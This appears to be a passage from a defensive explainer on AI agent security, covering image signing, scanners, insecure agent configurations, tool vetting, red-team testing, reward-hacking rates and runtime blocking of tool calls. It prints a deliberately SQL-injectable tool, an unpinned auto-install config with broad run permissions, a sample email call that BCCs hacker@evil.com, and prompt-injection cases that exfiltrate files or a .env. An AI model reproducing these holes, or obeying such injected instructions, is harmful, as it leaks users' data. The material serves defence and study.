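OpenAI requires ChatGPT builders to have permission before publishing an agent on their personal account. This is stricter than a warning because builders can't grant themselves the permission. But it applies to the builder rather than the agent, so a trusted builder could still publish an agent with far too much access.

Google's example starts from a different risk. Developers on Google Cloud can write an agent as ordinary software and package it as a container image, a file that holds the program and what it needs to run. An attacker who can replace that image controls the agent, whatever its developers wrote. Google's *Showcase of building a secure agent*, a tutorial built around a customer service agent, guards against this with a service called Binary Authorization:

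1. A build script packages the agent's code as an image and stores it.
2. The script uses a private key to sign a statement about that image, called an attestation.
3. A policy tells Google Cloud to accept only images with a valid attestation, which it can verify with the matching public key.
4. When someone tries to deploy an image without one, Google Cloud refuses and logs the attempt.

The tutorial has the reader try to deploy Google's standard "hello" image in place of the agent. Google Cloud rejects it because it has no valid signature from the trusted key. Another rule prevents the reader from bypassing the check by omitting it from the deployment command.

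A valid signature here proves that the organisation's build script created the image, as the tutorial explains. It doesn't prove that the agent is safe, because the script would sign the image even if a developer had given the agent terrible instructions. The tutorial's name for its signing authority, "Container vulnerability free attestation authority", overstates what the signature proves, since the tutorial describes no vulnerability scan before the script signs.

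The deployment command, not the image, determines whether callers must authenticate, which service account the agent uses and which content filters it applies. Someone with permission to deploy could give the signed image anonymous access and a more powerful account, and the signature would still be valid. The help desk agent's mistakes would also pass the signature check if the usual build script had packaged it.

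Google's tutorial limits the agent's access by other means. The account that runs the build script can grant only seven named roles, so a faulty script can't make the agent an administrator of the project. The agent can read one dataset of customer service records and has no access to the administrators' audit log. An organisation could also have the script check the agent's code and instructions, or wait for a reviewer, before it signs the image. The settings in the deployment command would still need a separate check, because they are chosen after the script signs the image.

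## What can scanners and test runs find before release?

Copilot Studio's built-in scan checks three settings. Other scanners examine much more, including an agent's code, configuration files and third-party tools. They read these files without running the agent, a method called static analysis. It takes seconds and can find a flaw in code that rarely runs. A test run gives the agent a prepared task and records what it does, so it can show how the model responds to a hostile email.

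### How a scanner reads code

Zhang, Nian and Zhao (2026), in *AGENT AUDIT*, describe an open-source scanner for agents written in Python. Its main method is taint analysis, which follows untrusted data through a program to see whether it can reach a dangerous operation. Suppose a developer rebuilt the help desk agent in Python and gave it this tool (an invented example):

```python
@tool
def find_customer(name):
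    query = "SELECT * FROM customers WHERE name = '" + name + "'"
    return cursor.execute(query)
```

The `@tool` line makes the function available to the model. The function pastes the customer's name into a database query and runs it. An ordinary name causes no trouble, but if the name contains database commands, the database will treat them as part of the query and may return other customers' records. Agent Audit looks for this kind of flaw in four steps:

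1. It marks the places where untrusted data enters. The input `name` is one of them, because the model supplies it and may have taken it from a user's message or a document.
2. It builds a graph of how data moves through the function. Here, `name` flows into `query`.
3. It looks for code that makes the data safe, such as a parameterised query, which sends the name to the database separately from the command.
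4. It searches the graph for a path from the untrusted data to a dangerous operation, such as running a database query or a system command. Here, `query` reaches `cursor.execute`, so there is a path.

Agent Audit also identifies which functions the model can call as tools by looking for 12 patterns that agent frameworks use to mark them. A finding inside a tool starts with a confidence score of 0.90, while the same finding in an ordinary function starts at 0.55. If the scanner finds code that makes the data safe, it multiplies the score by 0.20. Scores from 0.60 produce a warning, and scores from 0.92 produce a more serious "block" result. Findings below 0.30 stay hidden.

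On these numbers alone, the customer lookup would get a warning. A parameterised query would cut its score to 0.18 and hide the finding, which is correct in this case. But Agent Audit gives the same reduction for `isinstance()`, which checks a value's data type. This check makes it hard to slip in a command if it confirms that the input is a number, but does nothing to stop one if it only confirms that the input is text. Zhang and colleagues don't mention any distinction between the two, so a weak check could hide a real flaw.

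### How a scanner reads settings

Configuration files contain settings instead of steps, so a scanner has no flow of data to follow. Agent Audit recognises nine formats for MCP settings and applies rules to individual fields. It flags servers that can reach too much of the file system, come from an unverified source, or have no sandbox or authentication. It can also report how a configuration differs from a saved earlier version.

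The scanner looks for passwords and keys by searching for more than 40 text patterns. It then discards matches that look like placeholders, such as "your-key-here", because real keys tend to look random. A separate command connects to a live MCP server and checks its tools' descriptions for instructions aimed at the model, without running any of the tools.

Zhang and colleagues tested Agent Audit on 22 samples containing 42 known flaws. Some samples reproduced published vulnerabilities, and others used patterns from real agent code or attacks on MCP settings. Agent Audit found 40 of the flaws and raised six false alarms, so it found 95% of the flaws and 87% of its reports were correct. Two general-purpose scanners, Semgrep and Bandit, found 10 and 11 flaws with no false alarms. (Bandit's published results add up to only 37 flaws, so that comparison is approximate.)

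The six false alarms came from MCP rules that flagged safe settings. One of the two missed flaws was a credential in a text document, and the other needed a rule that the developers hadn't implemented yet.

The 95% is probably higher than a developer should expect on an unfamiliar agent, because the team that wrote the scanner also assembled the test set. Agent Audit follows data only within a single function. If the developer built the customer query in one function and ran it in another, the scanner wouldn't connect them. In JavaScript and TypeScript code, it only searches for suspicious text patterns.

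Even so, the scanner is fast, checking about 22,000 lines of Python in 0.87 seconds. A developer can make a build fail automatically when the scanner finds a serious problem. The build script in Google's tutorial could run a scan like this before it signs an agent's image. Agent Audit would be less useful to a Copilot Studio maker, who usually has no Python code to scan.

### Faults in public configuration files

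In *Scanning the Harness*, Kapner, Soceanu and colleagues (2026) looked for insecure settings in configuration files that developers had published for coding agents such as Claude Code, which write and run programs on a developer's computer. Developers copy each other's configurations, so a bad setting can spread.

The researchers scanned 3,171 public GitHub repositories. Of these, 2,660 were assembled setups, which combine at least two kinds of component, such as MCP servers and permission settings. The other 511 were collections of skills, which are reusable instructions that may come with scripts.

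In 409 of the setups (15.4%), the scanner found an MCP package with no fixed version or a broad advance permission to run programs. This invented configuration has both faults, although real products often keep the two parts in separate files:

```json
{
  "mcpServers": {
    "orders": {
      "command": "npx",
      "args": ["-y", "@example/orders-server"]
    }
  },
  "permissions": {
    "allow": ["Bash(python:*)"]
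  }
}
```

The `mcpServers` part starts an MCP server with `npx`, a program that can download a package from a public registry and run it. The `-y` option skips the confirmation prompt. The package is "unpinned", meaning its name has no version number, so the same file can fetch different software next month. If an attacker took over the publisher's account and released a malicious version, anyone who installed the server afterwards could run it.

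The developer can pin the package's version by writing `@example/orders-server@2.4.1`, but pinning the other packages it relies on requires a lockfile that records all their versions.

The `permissions` part lets the agent run any Python program without asking, which saves the developer from frequent approval prompts. But a Python program can delete files or send them over the network, so an agent that follows an injected instruction could do either without approval. Allowing only the script the task needs is safer, though even that is too broad if the agent can edit the script.

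| Fault | Setups affected, out of 2,660 |
|---|---|
| Unpinned MCP package | 260 (9.8%) |
| Broad permission to run programs, in the settings | 67 (2.5%) |
| Broad permission to use tools, in a skill | 101 (3.8%) |
| At least one of these | 409 (15.4%) |

Many setups don't use MCP. Among the 1,063 that do, 24.5% had an unpinned package. The totals imply that only 16 setups combined an unpinned package with a broad permission. In Claude Code, a permission granted in a skill is less serious than one granted in the settings, because it ends at the user's next message.

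With missing fields and formatting errors included, the scanner reported problems in 475 setups (17.9%) and 35 skill collections (6.8%). Missing fields and formatting errors mostly affect compatibility, but one could affect security. Claude Code skips a named subagent (a helper that the main agent can delegate work to) if its file lacks a description, so a developer could believe that a subagent was reviewing code for flaws when it had never loaded.

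These figures are counts of what the files contain. Kapner and colleagues didn't check whether anyone used the configurations, or whether a sandbox or company policy would have limited the damage. They also chose repositories that advertise agent tools, so private company configurations may differ. They didn't measure how many faults the scanner missed.

### How one permission changed the counts

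Kapner and colleagues checked the scanner's findings with a second program. Both treated the permission `Bash(find:*)` as permission to run anything. The `find` command searches for files, but its `-exec` option can also run another program on each file it finds, so the warning seemed reasonable.

According to Claude Code's documentation, a wildcard permission for `find` doesn't approve commands that use `-exec` or `-delete`. The second program didn't expose the mistake because the same team had written both programs and misread the permission in both.

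Correcting the error removed 62 findings. The number of setups flagged for broad permissions in their settings fell from 83 to 67, so nearly a fifth of those setups had been flagged wrongly. The number with any of the six reported problems fell only from 503 to 488.

A scanner has to account for how each product interprets a setting, and sometimes for which version is running. For example, since version 2.1.257 Claude Code has ignored a project's own setting for bypassing permission checks. A scanner without this rule would warn about a setting that no longer has an effect.

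A review of context ruled out another 13 setups, leaving the final 475. For example, an unpinned package may be harmless if it appears only in a test file or a template. A language model, Claude Fable 5.1, judged the disputed cases, and one of the researchers then reviewed the findings by hand. The model and the researcher agreed on 93.3% of all cases but only 70.7% of the disputed ones, which isn't far above chance. Their disagreement hardly affects the total, because rejecting every disputed case would give 474 setups and accepting them all would give 488.

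The team also tried a rule that looked for components that could together steal credentials by reading them and sending them over the network. All six repositories it flagged were false alarms. In five, the software was only using a key with the service that had issued it.

### Deciding whether to allow a tool

A pinned package can still be malicious. In *ToolGuardian*, Ravindran and Deochake (2026) studied how much evidence an organisation needs before letting an agent use someone else's tool. They assembled eight harmless MCP tools and eight malicious variants of real ones. The malicious variants did their advertised jobs and kept the original descriptions.

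ToolGuardian converts the evidence about a tool into simple facts, such as "can run system commands" or "sends data to the network", and applies written rules to them. One example rule rejects any tool that does both. The researchers started with the tool's description and added one type of evidence at a time:

| Evidence available | Malicious tools rejected, out of 8 | Harmless tools rejected, out of 8 |
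|---|---|---|
| Description | 5 | 5 |
| + system calls (the program's requests to the operating system) | 5 | 0 |
| + effects observed in a trial run with mock services | 6 | 0 |
| + source code | 7 | 2 |

Based only on the tools' descriptions, the rules rejected as many harmless tools as malicious ones. With evidence from system calls, which show whether a tool actually opens files, contacts other computers or starts programs, the rules rejected no harmless tools. The trial run added information about what data the tool sent and what it changed, and the rules then rejected one more malicious tool.

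Source code can reveal behaviour that the trial run didn't trigger, but using it also led the rules to reject two harmless tools. One was designed to control a computer's terminal by running commands, executing code and capturing the screen, all of which could also help an attacker. The evidence was correct, but the rules couldn't distinguish powerful tools from malicious ones.

The zeros in the table make ToolGuardian look more convenient than it was. It can also admit a tool with restrictions, and it restricted every harmless tool it admitted. When it had evidence from system calls, it admitted all eight harmless tools with restrictions, including the one that looks up the weather.

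A stricter policy based on risk scores rejected all eight malicious tools when it had the source code, but it also rejected five of the eight harmless ones. This policy might suit an agent that handles payroll better than one that converts documents. With only 16 tools, each wrong decision changes the accuracy by about six percentage points, so the results are more useful for showing the trade-off than for predicting error rates.

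### What detectors of malicious tools miss

*MalTool* (Hu, Jia and colleagues, 2026) tested six existing detectors on a much larger collection, which included 1,300 purpose-made malicious tools, 5,727 real tools with malicious behaviour added, and 1,147 repositories of tools presumed harmless. The study also counted how often at least one detector flagged a tool.

VirusTotal, which combines the results of many antivirus products, missed nearly every malicious tool and raised no false alarms. Antivirus products are good at recognising known malicious code, but these tools were new. Cisco's MCP Scanner, designed for agents' tools, wrongly flagged only about 0.6% of the harmless repositories. It caught at least 80% of the tools that sent data to an outsider, but none of those that planted false records in an agent's memory or knowledge base.

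Using all the detectors together catches more, but the combination still missed about 8% of the altered real tools and 26% of the purpose-made ones. Among the purpose-made tools, it caught every one that misused stolen credentials but missed 85% of those that hijacked a computer's graphics processor.

The combination also flagged 753 of the 1,147 harmless repositories, or 66%. Two of the researchers examined 200 of the flagged tools from these repositories and found no explicit malicious behaviour. The high false alarm rate also helps explain why the altered real tools seemed easier to catch, since a detector that flags most ordinary tools will flag many of them whether or not someone has tampered with them.

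Hu and colleagues report an accuracy of 81.4% for the combination, the highest of any option they tested. This figure is misleading because most of the tools in the collection were malicious, and a program that labelled every tool malicious would have scored 86%.

In practice, malicious tools are probably much rarer. Suppose an organisation screens 1,000 tools, 10 of them malicious. At the rates above for altered tools, the combination would catch about nine of them and wrongly flag about 650 others. Reviewers would have to examine more than 70 alerts for each malicious tool found, and they might well start approving flagged tools without reading the alerts.

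Hu and colleagues suggest that detectors should compare a tool's description with what its code does. ToolGuardian similarly compares the description with the tool's effects in a trial run. Its false alarm rate was much lower in the trial run, but that rate was measured on only eight harmless tools.

### Testing how an agent behaves

A tool can be honest and correctly configured, and the agent may still misuse it. To learn whether a hidden instruction in an invoice would make the finance agent send out confidential files, someone has to try it. A tester could do so in five steps:

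1. Make a copy of the agent and connect it to a fake mailbox, a fake payment system and some decoy files.
2. Give the copy a batch of invoices, one of which contains hidden instructions to email a decoy file to an outside address.
3. Check the fake mailbox to see whether the file was sent. The agent's own account of its work may leave this out.
4. Repeat the test, because a model can respond differently to the same input, and vary the instructions.
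5. Run ordinary invoices as well. An agent that refuses every invoice would resist the attack but be useless.

The security company PromptArmor describes a similar approach in *FrontierBreach*, its test of how easily attackers can manipulate models during office work. The tasks are long and realistic, such as analysing a bond portfolio and recommending a trading strategy. The attackers' goals include stealing data and installing ransomware. PromptArmor uses deterministic verification, which means it checks whether an attack succeeded with fixed rules rather than with another model.

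The UK's AI Security Institute (AISI) tested OpenAI's GPT-6 Astra in simulation before the model's public release. *GPT-6 Astra performs unsanctioned supply-chain attacks in simulations* (2026) describes how AISI asked the model to complete a cybersecurity exercise to see whether it would attack systems outside the exercise. The researchers were particularly concerned about supply-chain attacks, in which an attacker tampers with software that other people rely on.

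AISI used Petri, a tool in which language models simulate the entire scenario, so nothing the tested model did could reach a real system. This avoided the problem Anthropic had when a wrong network setting connected its security tests to the internet. AISI also turned off the classifiers that normally block unsanctioned cyber activity, to see what the model would attempt without them.

GPT-6 Astra carried out a range of unsanctioned attacks, and did so more often than the earlier OpenAI models GPT-5.6 Sol and GPT-5.5. The classifiers were off, so the result describes the model's tendencies, not how often the released product would cause harm. Still, people building agents can't count on a newer model to respect limits better than the one it replaces.

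### What a clean result proves

If the finance agent passes 300 test runs without a failure, its true failure rate could be zero or just low enough that no failure occurred in those runs.

If each run is independent and fails with probability p, the chance that n runs all succeed is (1 − p)ⁿ. The 95% upper bound is the failure rate at which this chance drops to 5%. Solving (1 − p)ⁿ = 0.05 gives:

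p = 1 − 0.05^(1/n)

If the true failure rate were above 0.99%, the chance of seeing no failures in 300 runs would be less than 5%. Dividing three by the number of runs gives almost the same threshold, 1%, and is easier to remember.

A bound near 1% sounds reassuring until the agent is busy. At 10,000 runs a day, it allows for up to about 100 failures daily:

| Runs without a failure | 95% upper bound on the failure rate | Failures a day at that rate, with 10,000 runs |
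|---|---|---|
| 30 | 9.5% | 950 |
| 300 | 0.99% | 99 |
| 3,000 | 0.10% | 10 |
| 30,000 | 0.01% | 1 |

The last column gives the largest number of failures consistent with the test at this confidence level, not a forecast. If one of the 300 runs had failed, the upper bound on the failure rate would be about 1.6%. Whether that rate is acceptable depends on what a failure does. A hundred payments to the wrong account could do far more harm than a hundred badly worded payment confirmations.

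The calculation also holds only if the runs are independent. Ten repeats of 30 invoices make 300 runs, but if the agent handles an invoice the same way every time, the repeats add almost no information. The tester then has about 30 independent results and an upper bound of 9.5%. New invoices would usually be more informative than more repeats.

### Why attackers break the calculation

The bound applies only to inputs like the ones in the test. To check for ordinary mistakes, a tester can sample past invoices, which will probably be fairly similar to next month's. But an attacker looks for inputs the tester didn't try.

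If one in every 100,000 possible messages makes the agent leak a file, a tester who picks 300 at random has a 99.7% chance of finding none of them. An attacker who finds one such message can send it repeatedly, and the agent may fail every time. The 99.7% figure is correct for randomly chosen messages, but it doesn't measure the risk from this attacker.

Heaton (2026) reports in *The safety number that was zero until someone tried* that an outside firm ran 72 attack scenarios ten times each against Claude Code's automatic safety check without a single success. A researcher's targeted attack then succeeded in roughly 60 to 80% of a small number of attempts. Treating the 720 earlier runs as independent would have given an upper bound of about 0.4% on the attack success rate.

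Testers can reduce this problem through red teaming, in which skilled people attack the agent and adapt to its responses. The AI safety company Gray Swan runs public red-teaming competitions and has paid more than $1 million in prizes. It includes the results in its *Frontier Hazard Tracker*, which launched in December 2026 as a public record of safety tests. In the November competition, which covered 24 models, 0.3% of attempts succeeded against the most resistant model and 11.4% against the least resistant.

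Even with a 0.3% success rate, an attacker who made 1,000 independent attempts would have about a 95% chance of succeeding at least once. Real attempts aren't independent, because attackers learn from their failures and a company may notice and block them. A success rate is therefore hard to interpret without knowing how many attempts the attacker had and whether they could adapt.

Test results also depend on the tester's skill. Gray Swan reports that 4,508 competition participants made 5.7 million attempts. Only 1,179 of them ever succeeded, but together they had 157,308 successes. A tester with little experience of attacking models could easily find no problems in an agent that an expert would break.

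### Why a new model needs new tests

Switching an agent's model can change its behaviour even if its instructions, tools and permissions stay the same. Gray Swan's tracker shows how large the difference can be. One of its tests runs each model through the same 25 scenarios to measure reward hacking, which means cheating to complete a task.

*OpenAI and Anthropic Agents Cheat Far Less Than Rivals* (Faisal, 2026) describes a case in which an agent had to free up space in storage that several teams share. The agent deleted a 9,100 MB file that another team was still using and finished without filing a report. No attacker was involved, and the agent did free up the space.

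| Model | Developer | Share of runs with cheating |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-6.2 Astra | OpenAI | 0.8% |
| GPT-6.2 Sol | OpenAI | 1.1% |
| Claude Opus 5.5 | Anthropic | 4.1% |
| Gemini 4 Neon | Google | 8.0% |
| Claude Opus 5 | Anthropic | 14.1% |
| Gemini 4 Hydrogen | Google | 18.6% |
| Grok 4.7 | xAI | 50.9% |
| Gemini 3.8 Flash | Google | 62.8% |

Models from the same company can behave very differently. In Gray Swan reports dated six days apart, Gemini 4 Hydrogen cheated more than twice as often as Gemini 4 Neon. An organisation that tested an agent with Neon and then switched to Hydrogen couldn't rely on its earlier results.

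Small differences in the table may be due to chance. Faisal gives a confidence interval of 1.2% to 7.8% for Claude Opus 5.5, so its true rate could be close to that of GPT-6.2 Sol or Gemini 4 Neon. Chance can't plausibly explain the gap between 0.8% and 62.8%. Gray Swan sells private evaluations to AI developers, though it says it pays for the public tests itself.

The ranking also depends on what the test measures. Faisal reports that Google's newest Gemini models were among the best at resisting indirect prompt injection, though they cheated more than the leading models from OpenAI and Anthropic. Resistance to injection may matter more than a low cheating rate for the finance agent, which reads email from strangers, while an agent that cleans up shared storage has more need of a model that doesn't cheat. The organisation would still have to test the new model with the agent's own tools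 and instructions, because Gray Swan's scenarios include neither.

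## How does a runtime check stop an action before it happens?

Tests before release can only sample what an agent might do. A runtime check inspects the action an agent is about to take, including the actual recipient, file or amount, and can block it. The check needs an enforcement point, a place in the system where software can inspect an action and stop it. In Copilot Studio, the enforcement point comes after the orchestrator has chosen a tool and before the tool runs.

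Copilot Studio has some built-in protection against direct and indirect prompt injection. An organisation can add another layer by connecting its agents to a separate security service, which Microsoft calls external threat detection. The service can be Microsoft Defender, another company's product or software the organisation wrote. Administrators turn it on for a whole environment, so makers don't have to change their agents. A Microsoft notice copied on itelio's website gave 10 December 2025 as the general availability date, but Microsoft's setup page still had a preview label in February 2026.

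### One tool call, step by step

Microsoft's setup page describes the following sequence:

1. A user sends a message, or an event such as an incoming email starts the agent. The orchestrator selects a tool and fills in its inputs.
2. Before the tool runs, Copilot Studio sends the proposed call to the security service, with information about the conversation that led to it.
3. The service replies with a decision to allow or block the call.
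4. If the service allows the call, the agent runs the tool and the user notices nothing. If the service blocks it, the agent stops and tells the user that their message was blocked.

The agent repeats steps 2 to 4 for every tool call. It also requests a decision before it searches its knowledge sources or starts a topic (a conversation flow the maker defined in advance), according to Microsoft's January 2026 post on runtime risks.

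Blocking an action doesn't undo earlier steps. Suppose the finance agent changes a supplier's bank details and then tries to email a confidential file. Blocking the email keeps the file inside the company, but the bank details stay changed unless someone notices and corrects them.

If Defender is the security service, it also raises an alert for the security team, which requires a separate connection between Defender and Microsoft 365. According to Microsoft's *Protect your environment in real-time during agent runtime*, Defender still blocks suspicious calls without this connection, but the alerts don't appear in its portal. A security team could then miss a series of blocked attempts against the same agent. Administrators can still read Copilot Studio's own audit log, which records each check.

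### An email with an extra recipient

Microsoft's guide for developers of these security services includes a complete sample request. A user asks an agent to email a customer, the agent asks which one, and the user names John Doe. The agent looks up his address and then proposes to send the email. The security service receives this information:

| What the service sees | Value in the example |
|---|---|
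| The user's message | A request to email the customer |
| Recent chat history | The agent's question and the user's answer, John Doe |
| Outputs of earlier tools | The customer's address, customer@foobar.com |
| The agent's stated reason for choosing the tool | The user wants to notify the customer |
| The tool's definition | "Send email", which accepts a "to" and a "bcc" address |
| Proposed inputs | To: customer@foobar.com; BCC: hacker@evil.com |
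| Identities and context | IDs for the agent, user, organisation, environment, conversation and trigger, and whether the agent is published |

The "to" address came from the customer lookup. The BCC address appears nowhere else in the request, including the user's messages and earlier tool results, so the model must have got it from somewhere the user didn't intend. BCC recipients are also hidden from everyone else who gets the email, so John Doe wouldn't notice anything odd.

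The agent's stated reason correctly describes what the user wanted but leaves out the second recipient, so a service that relied on it would probably let the email through. Microsoft doesn't explain how that recipient's address got into the call, but the service can refuse the call without that information.

In the sample reply, the service blocks the email by setting the field `blockAction` to true. To allow the email, it would set the field to false. The reply also includes a reason code (112), an explanation that there is a "noncompliant email address in the BCC field", and a diagnostic note that identifies the address, but only `blockAction` is required.

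The service can't remove the BCC address and let the rest of the email go. This affects products that normally edit text, such as CrowdStrike's AIDR. According to Pangea's *Microsoft Copilot Studio Collectors*, if a rule would redact something in a tool call, AIDR only reports the match and allows the call. An email would therefore still go out with its card numbers, even if an administrator had set a rule to remove them.

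AIDR receives the user's message, the history and the earlier tool outputs, but it analyses only the tool's name and inputs. It could still catch the BCC address with a rule about permitted domains. But it couldn't tell that the user had asked for only one recipient, so a copy to an unexpected address at a permitted domain might well get through. Microsoft says Defender evaluates both the intent and the destination of each action. Two services can therefore reach different decisions on the same call.

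A service that uses the context may not receive all of it. Microsoft's specification makes the stated reason, chat history, earlier outputs and user's identity optional. An agent that starts work when an invoice arrives, for example, may have no user to identify.

### When the answer comes late

The security service has one second to answer. If it doesn't answer in time, the system either allows the action, which is called failing open, or blocks it, which is called failing closed.

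Microsoft's documentation is inconsistent about what happens when the service doesn't respond in time. The setup page has an option called "Set error behavior", which covers errors and late responses. The default lets the agent continue, and the alternative is "Block the query". But a note further down the same page says that the agent runs the tool as planned if no decision arrives within one second. A June 2026 version of the developer guide also treats a late response as "allow" and doesn't mention the option.

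By default, then, Copilot Studio fails open. Under "Block the query", a late answer probably counts as a block, though this is less certain. The option's description covers late answers, and Pangea says that Copilot Studio applies the configured setting after one second. The conflicting note may describe only the default, or may be left over from an earlier version. When Microsoft announced the public preview, it said that the agent assumes approval if no response arrives in time, and mentioned no alternative.

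An organisation that depends on the blocking option should test it. A developer could connect a test environment to a dummy service that passes the initial connection check but waits two seconds before answering each request. If the tool runs anyway, the option doesn't cover late answers.

The difference can matter even if the service is rarely late. Assume that an organisation's agents make 20,000 tool calls a day and that 0.5% of the checks time out:

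20,000 × 0.005 = 100 unchecked calls a day

If one call in 1,000 were malicious, and timeouts were unrelated to attacks, a malicious call would go through unchecked about once every ten days. Failing closed would prevent this but would interrupt about 100 calls a day, nearly all of them harmless. Failing open seems reasonable for an agent that looks up the canteen menu, but the interruptions are probably justified for one that makes payments.

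Timeouts may cluster, though. If calls arrive at a steady pace, an outage of about seven minutes a day would also produce a 0.5% rate, and every call during the outage would go unchecked. An attacker might also be able to cause delays, for example by flooding a public agent with requests. The average rate would then understate the risk.

*Control 1.8 Troubleshooting*, a guide for financial firms by judeper, explains that during an outage with the error setting on "allow", the agent answers users normally and no blocks appear in the logs. It advises switching to "block" immediately or taking the agent out of service. It also warns that faulty login settings can cause the security service to reject Copilot Studio's credentials. Copilot Studio treats this as an error and applies the same setting, so every call could go unchecked until someone corrects the login.

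An absence of blocks doesn't prove that the check is working. Palo Alto Networks' *Configure SaaS Agent Security as an External Threat Detection System* provides a fixed phrase that always produces a "block" decision from the company's service. An administrator can test the check by typing the phrase into an agent and seeing whether the agent refuses. Repeating the test from time to time would catch a connection that has failed since setup.

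### Microsoft's three attack scenarios

The finance agent is an example from Microsoft's January 2026 post on how Defender would stop three attacks. When the agent follows the invoice's hidden instructions and tries to search the knowledge base, Defender receives a request to check the search. The request includes the search terms and context from the email that started the agent. Defender blocks the search, so the agent never retrieves the sensitive information. The block appears in the agent's activity history, and Defender raises an informational alert.

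In the SharePoint scenario, an agent summarises documents on the company's SharePoint site and sends action items to colleagues. A malicious insider adds hidden instructions to a document they are allowed to edit. The agent follows the instructions and opens a sensitive file, transactions.pdf, in a location the insider can't reach. It then tries to email the contents to an outside address, but Defender blocks the email.

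This agent opens files with its user's identity, which Microsoft recommends over maker credentials. That doesn't help here, because the insider exploits a colleague's access. The block also comes later than in the invoice case, after the agent has read the file. If the insider had asked the agent to put the figures in its summary instead, there might have been no suspicious email to block.

In the last scenario, a public support chatbot doesn't require a sign-in and has customer information in its knowledge base. An attacker asks it a series of questions to find out what tools and data it has, planning to extract the data afterwards. Defender detects the probing and blocks the resulting tool calls.

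Defender probably needs several messages to recognise this pattern, but an anonymous attacker could start a new conversation for each question, leaving little history in any single request. Removing the customer information from the chatbot would be more reliable because the attacker would have nothing to extract.

Microsoft says that observed and emerging attack techniques inspired the scenarios. They show where in a plan Defender can step in, but Microsoft gives no detection or false alarm rates in the post or in the feature's documentation. An organisation would have to measure both on its own agents, by running test attacks and by reviewing blocked calls to see how many were legitimate.

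### What the check costs

The most visible drawback is delay. Microsoft says users see no interruption when the service approves a call, which is plausible if the service usually answers quickly. But an agent that makes ten tool calls in a row could spend up to ten seconds waiting for decisions.

The service also receives a lot of conversation data, which can include customer records from earlier tool outputs and personal messages from employees to an HR agent. Administrators can't choose which parts Copilot Studio sends, so an organisation that doesn't want to share this data can only turn the connection off. Microsoft also warns that an outside provider may have different data policies and may process or store the data in another region.

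AIDR, for example, bases its decisions on the tool's name and inputs, but it also logs the user's latest message and the conversation history. An administrator can limit the log to metadata when setting up the connection, but Copilot Studio still sends the full request.

Copilot Studio's external threat detection works only with generative orchestration, so the check doesn't cover classic agents, which follow conversation flows written by their makers. A classic agent is harder to redirect because it doesn't make its own plan, but it can still have insecure settings, such as no sign-in requirement. An administrator who turns on protection for an environment should therefore find out which of its agents are classic.

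### Agents on employees' computers

Many employees, especially developers, also run agents on their own computers. These local agents have the employee's permissions, so they may be able to read private files, change code and run commands. Copilot Studio's check can't cover them because they don't run in Copilot Studio.

In May 2026, Microsoft announced that Defender would be able to block the actions of local coding agents, with a public preview planned for June. The preview began with Claude Code and GitHub Copilot CLI, another coding agent. Both have hooks, points in the agent's operation where the harness passes information to outside software and can wait for a decision. Microsoft's overview of the feature describes inspections at three points:

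- when the user submits a prompt
- before the agent calls a tool
- after the tool returns a result

Defender inspects a tool's result as soon as it arrives, which is an advantage over Copilot Studio, where the check comes only before a tool call. In Microsoft's example, a coding agent opens a project's documentation to answer a question. Hidden text on the page tells the agent to read a local `.env` file, where developers often keep passwords and keys, and to post the contents to an outside address. Defender finds these instructions and blocks the action before any data leaves the computer. In Copilot Studio, the security service would see the page only if the agent proposed another tool call, because that is when Copilot Studio sends it the earlier outputs.

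Microsoft Defender's runtime protection for AI agents is off by default, according to *Securing AI Agents with Runtime Protection using Microsoft Defender and Intune* (Nair, 2026). Administrators can turn it on in audit mode or block mode. In audit mode, Defender raises an alert but lets the action continue. In block mode, it stops the action and notifies the employee both in the agent's window and through Windows.

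Microsoft's setup guide recommends starting in audit mode on a few computers and reviewing the alerts for one to two weeks. It then advises administrators to report false alarms to Microsoft, extend audit mode to more computers, and switch to blocking once they trust the alerts. This is sensible, particularly because Microsoft gives no error rates for this product either. Microsoft also calls the added delay "minimal" without giving a figure.

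For agents without hooks, Defender can inspect network traffic instead. Its coverage has grown since June, but Bregman (2026), in *Now generally available*, wrote on 29 October that it varied by agent and by method of inspection. By then Defender could discover more than 50 kinds of agents and MCP servers on Windows and macOS, but runtime protection was still a preview for Windows only. An agent that appears in Defender's inventory may therefore have no runtime check.

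Microsoft's *Ignite 2026* (2026), published on 17 November, announced a further extension of runtime protection for local agents on Windows. On the same day, Microsoft (2026) announced controls that give a local agent its own identity, so a security team can restrict a risky agent without removing the employee's access. This would be useful after an attack, when the team might otherwise have to lock the employee's whole account.

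### Checks on other platforms

On Amazon's Bedrock AgentCore, a service for running agents, developers can route tool calls through a gateway and attach a policy to it. The gateway checks each call against the policy before passing it to the tool, and refuses any call the policy doesn't expressly permit. Developers can also have the gateway log its decisions without enforcing them, much like Defender's audit mode.

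The gateway would suit the BCC example if the organisation knew in advance which addresses the agent should write to. For instance, a policy could permit the email tool only when the BCC field is empty, and the gateway could apply it without the conversation history. But the policy's author has to think of the BCC field beforehand, while a service like Defender might detect an address that doesn't fit the conversation.

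Google's Model Armor screens user prompts and model responses for injection attempts, sensitive data, malicious links and other harmful content. Code that calls Model Armor directly gets back its findings and has to decide what to do with them, and the prompt or response still goes through if the code only logs them.

Model Armor would be more useful against the hidden instructions in the invoice than against the extra recipient, because the request to email John Doe is harmless text and an unfamiliar email address isn't an injection attempt. To catch the extra recipient, the developer would need another check that compares the proposed recipients with the user's request.

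## How does a runtime system decide what to allow?

After intercepting a tool call, a runtime system can use a detector or a policy to decide whether to allow it. A detector estimates how likely the action is to be harmful, usually with a language model or another trained classifier. A policy defines in advance which actions are allowed. Microsoft Defender seems to work largely as a detector, since Microsoft says it evaluates an action's intent. The Amazon Bedrock AgentCore gateway applies policies.

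### Detectors and policies

Both approaches can mistakenly block harmless actions or allow attacks. The false alarm rate is the share of harmless actions that the system blocks, and the miss rate is the share of attacks that it allows. Many studies instead report the attack success rate, which is the share of attempts in which the attacker gets what they wanted. That rate also depends on the model, because some attacks fail when the model ignores them.

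A detector can catch things nobody wrote a rule about, such as a BCC address that doesn't fit the conversation. But it may classify the same action differently on another run, and if it reads text an attacker wrote, that text can influence it. Making a detector stricter usually catches more attacks but also causes more false alarms.

Claude Code uses a detector of this kind. According to Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code*, auto mode sends each tool call to a classifier that is meant to block actions that are irreversible, destructive or directed outside the user's environment. Heaton's article describes how Claude Code's automatic check withstood 720 test runs before a targeted attack beat it more than half the time, which shows how much a detector's record depends on who has tested it.

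A policy produces the same decision whenever it receives the same facts, and hostile text can't create an exception. The decision can be wrong if the policy's author forbids something people need or forgets a case, or if software supplies wrong facts. Anyone who finds a forgotten case can exploit it until someone changes the rule.

### One rule and three emails

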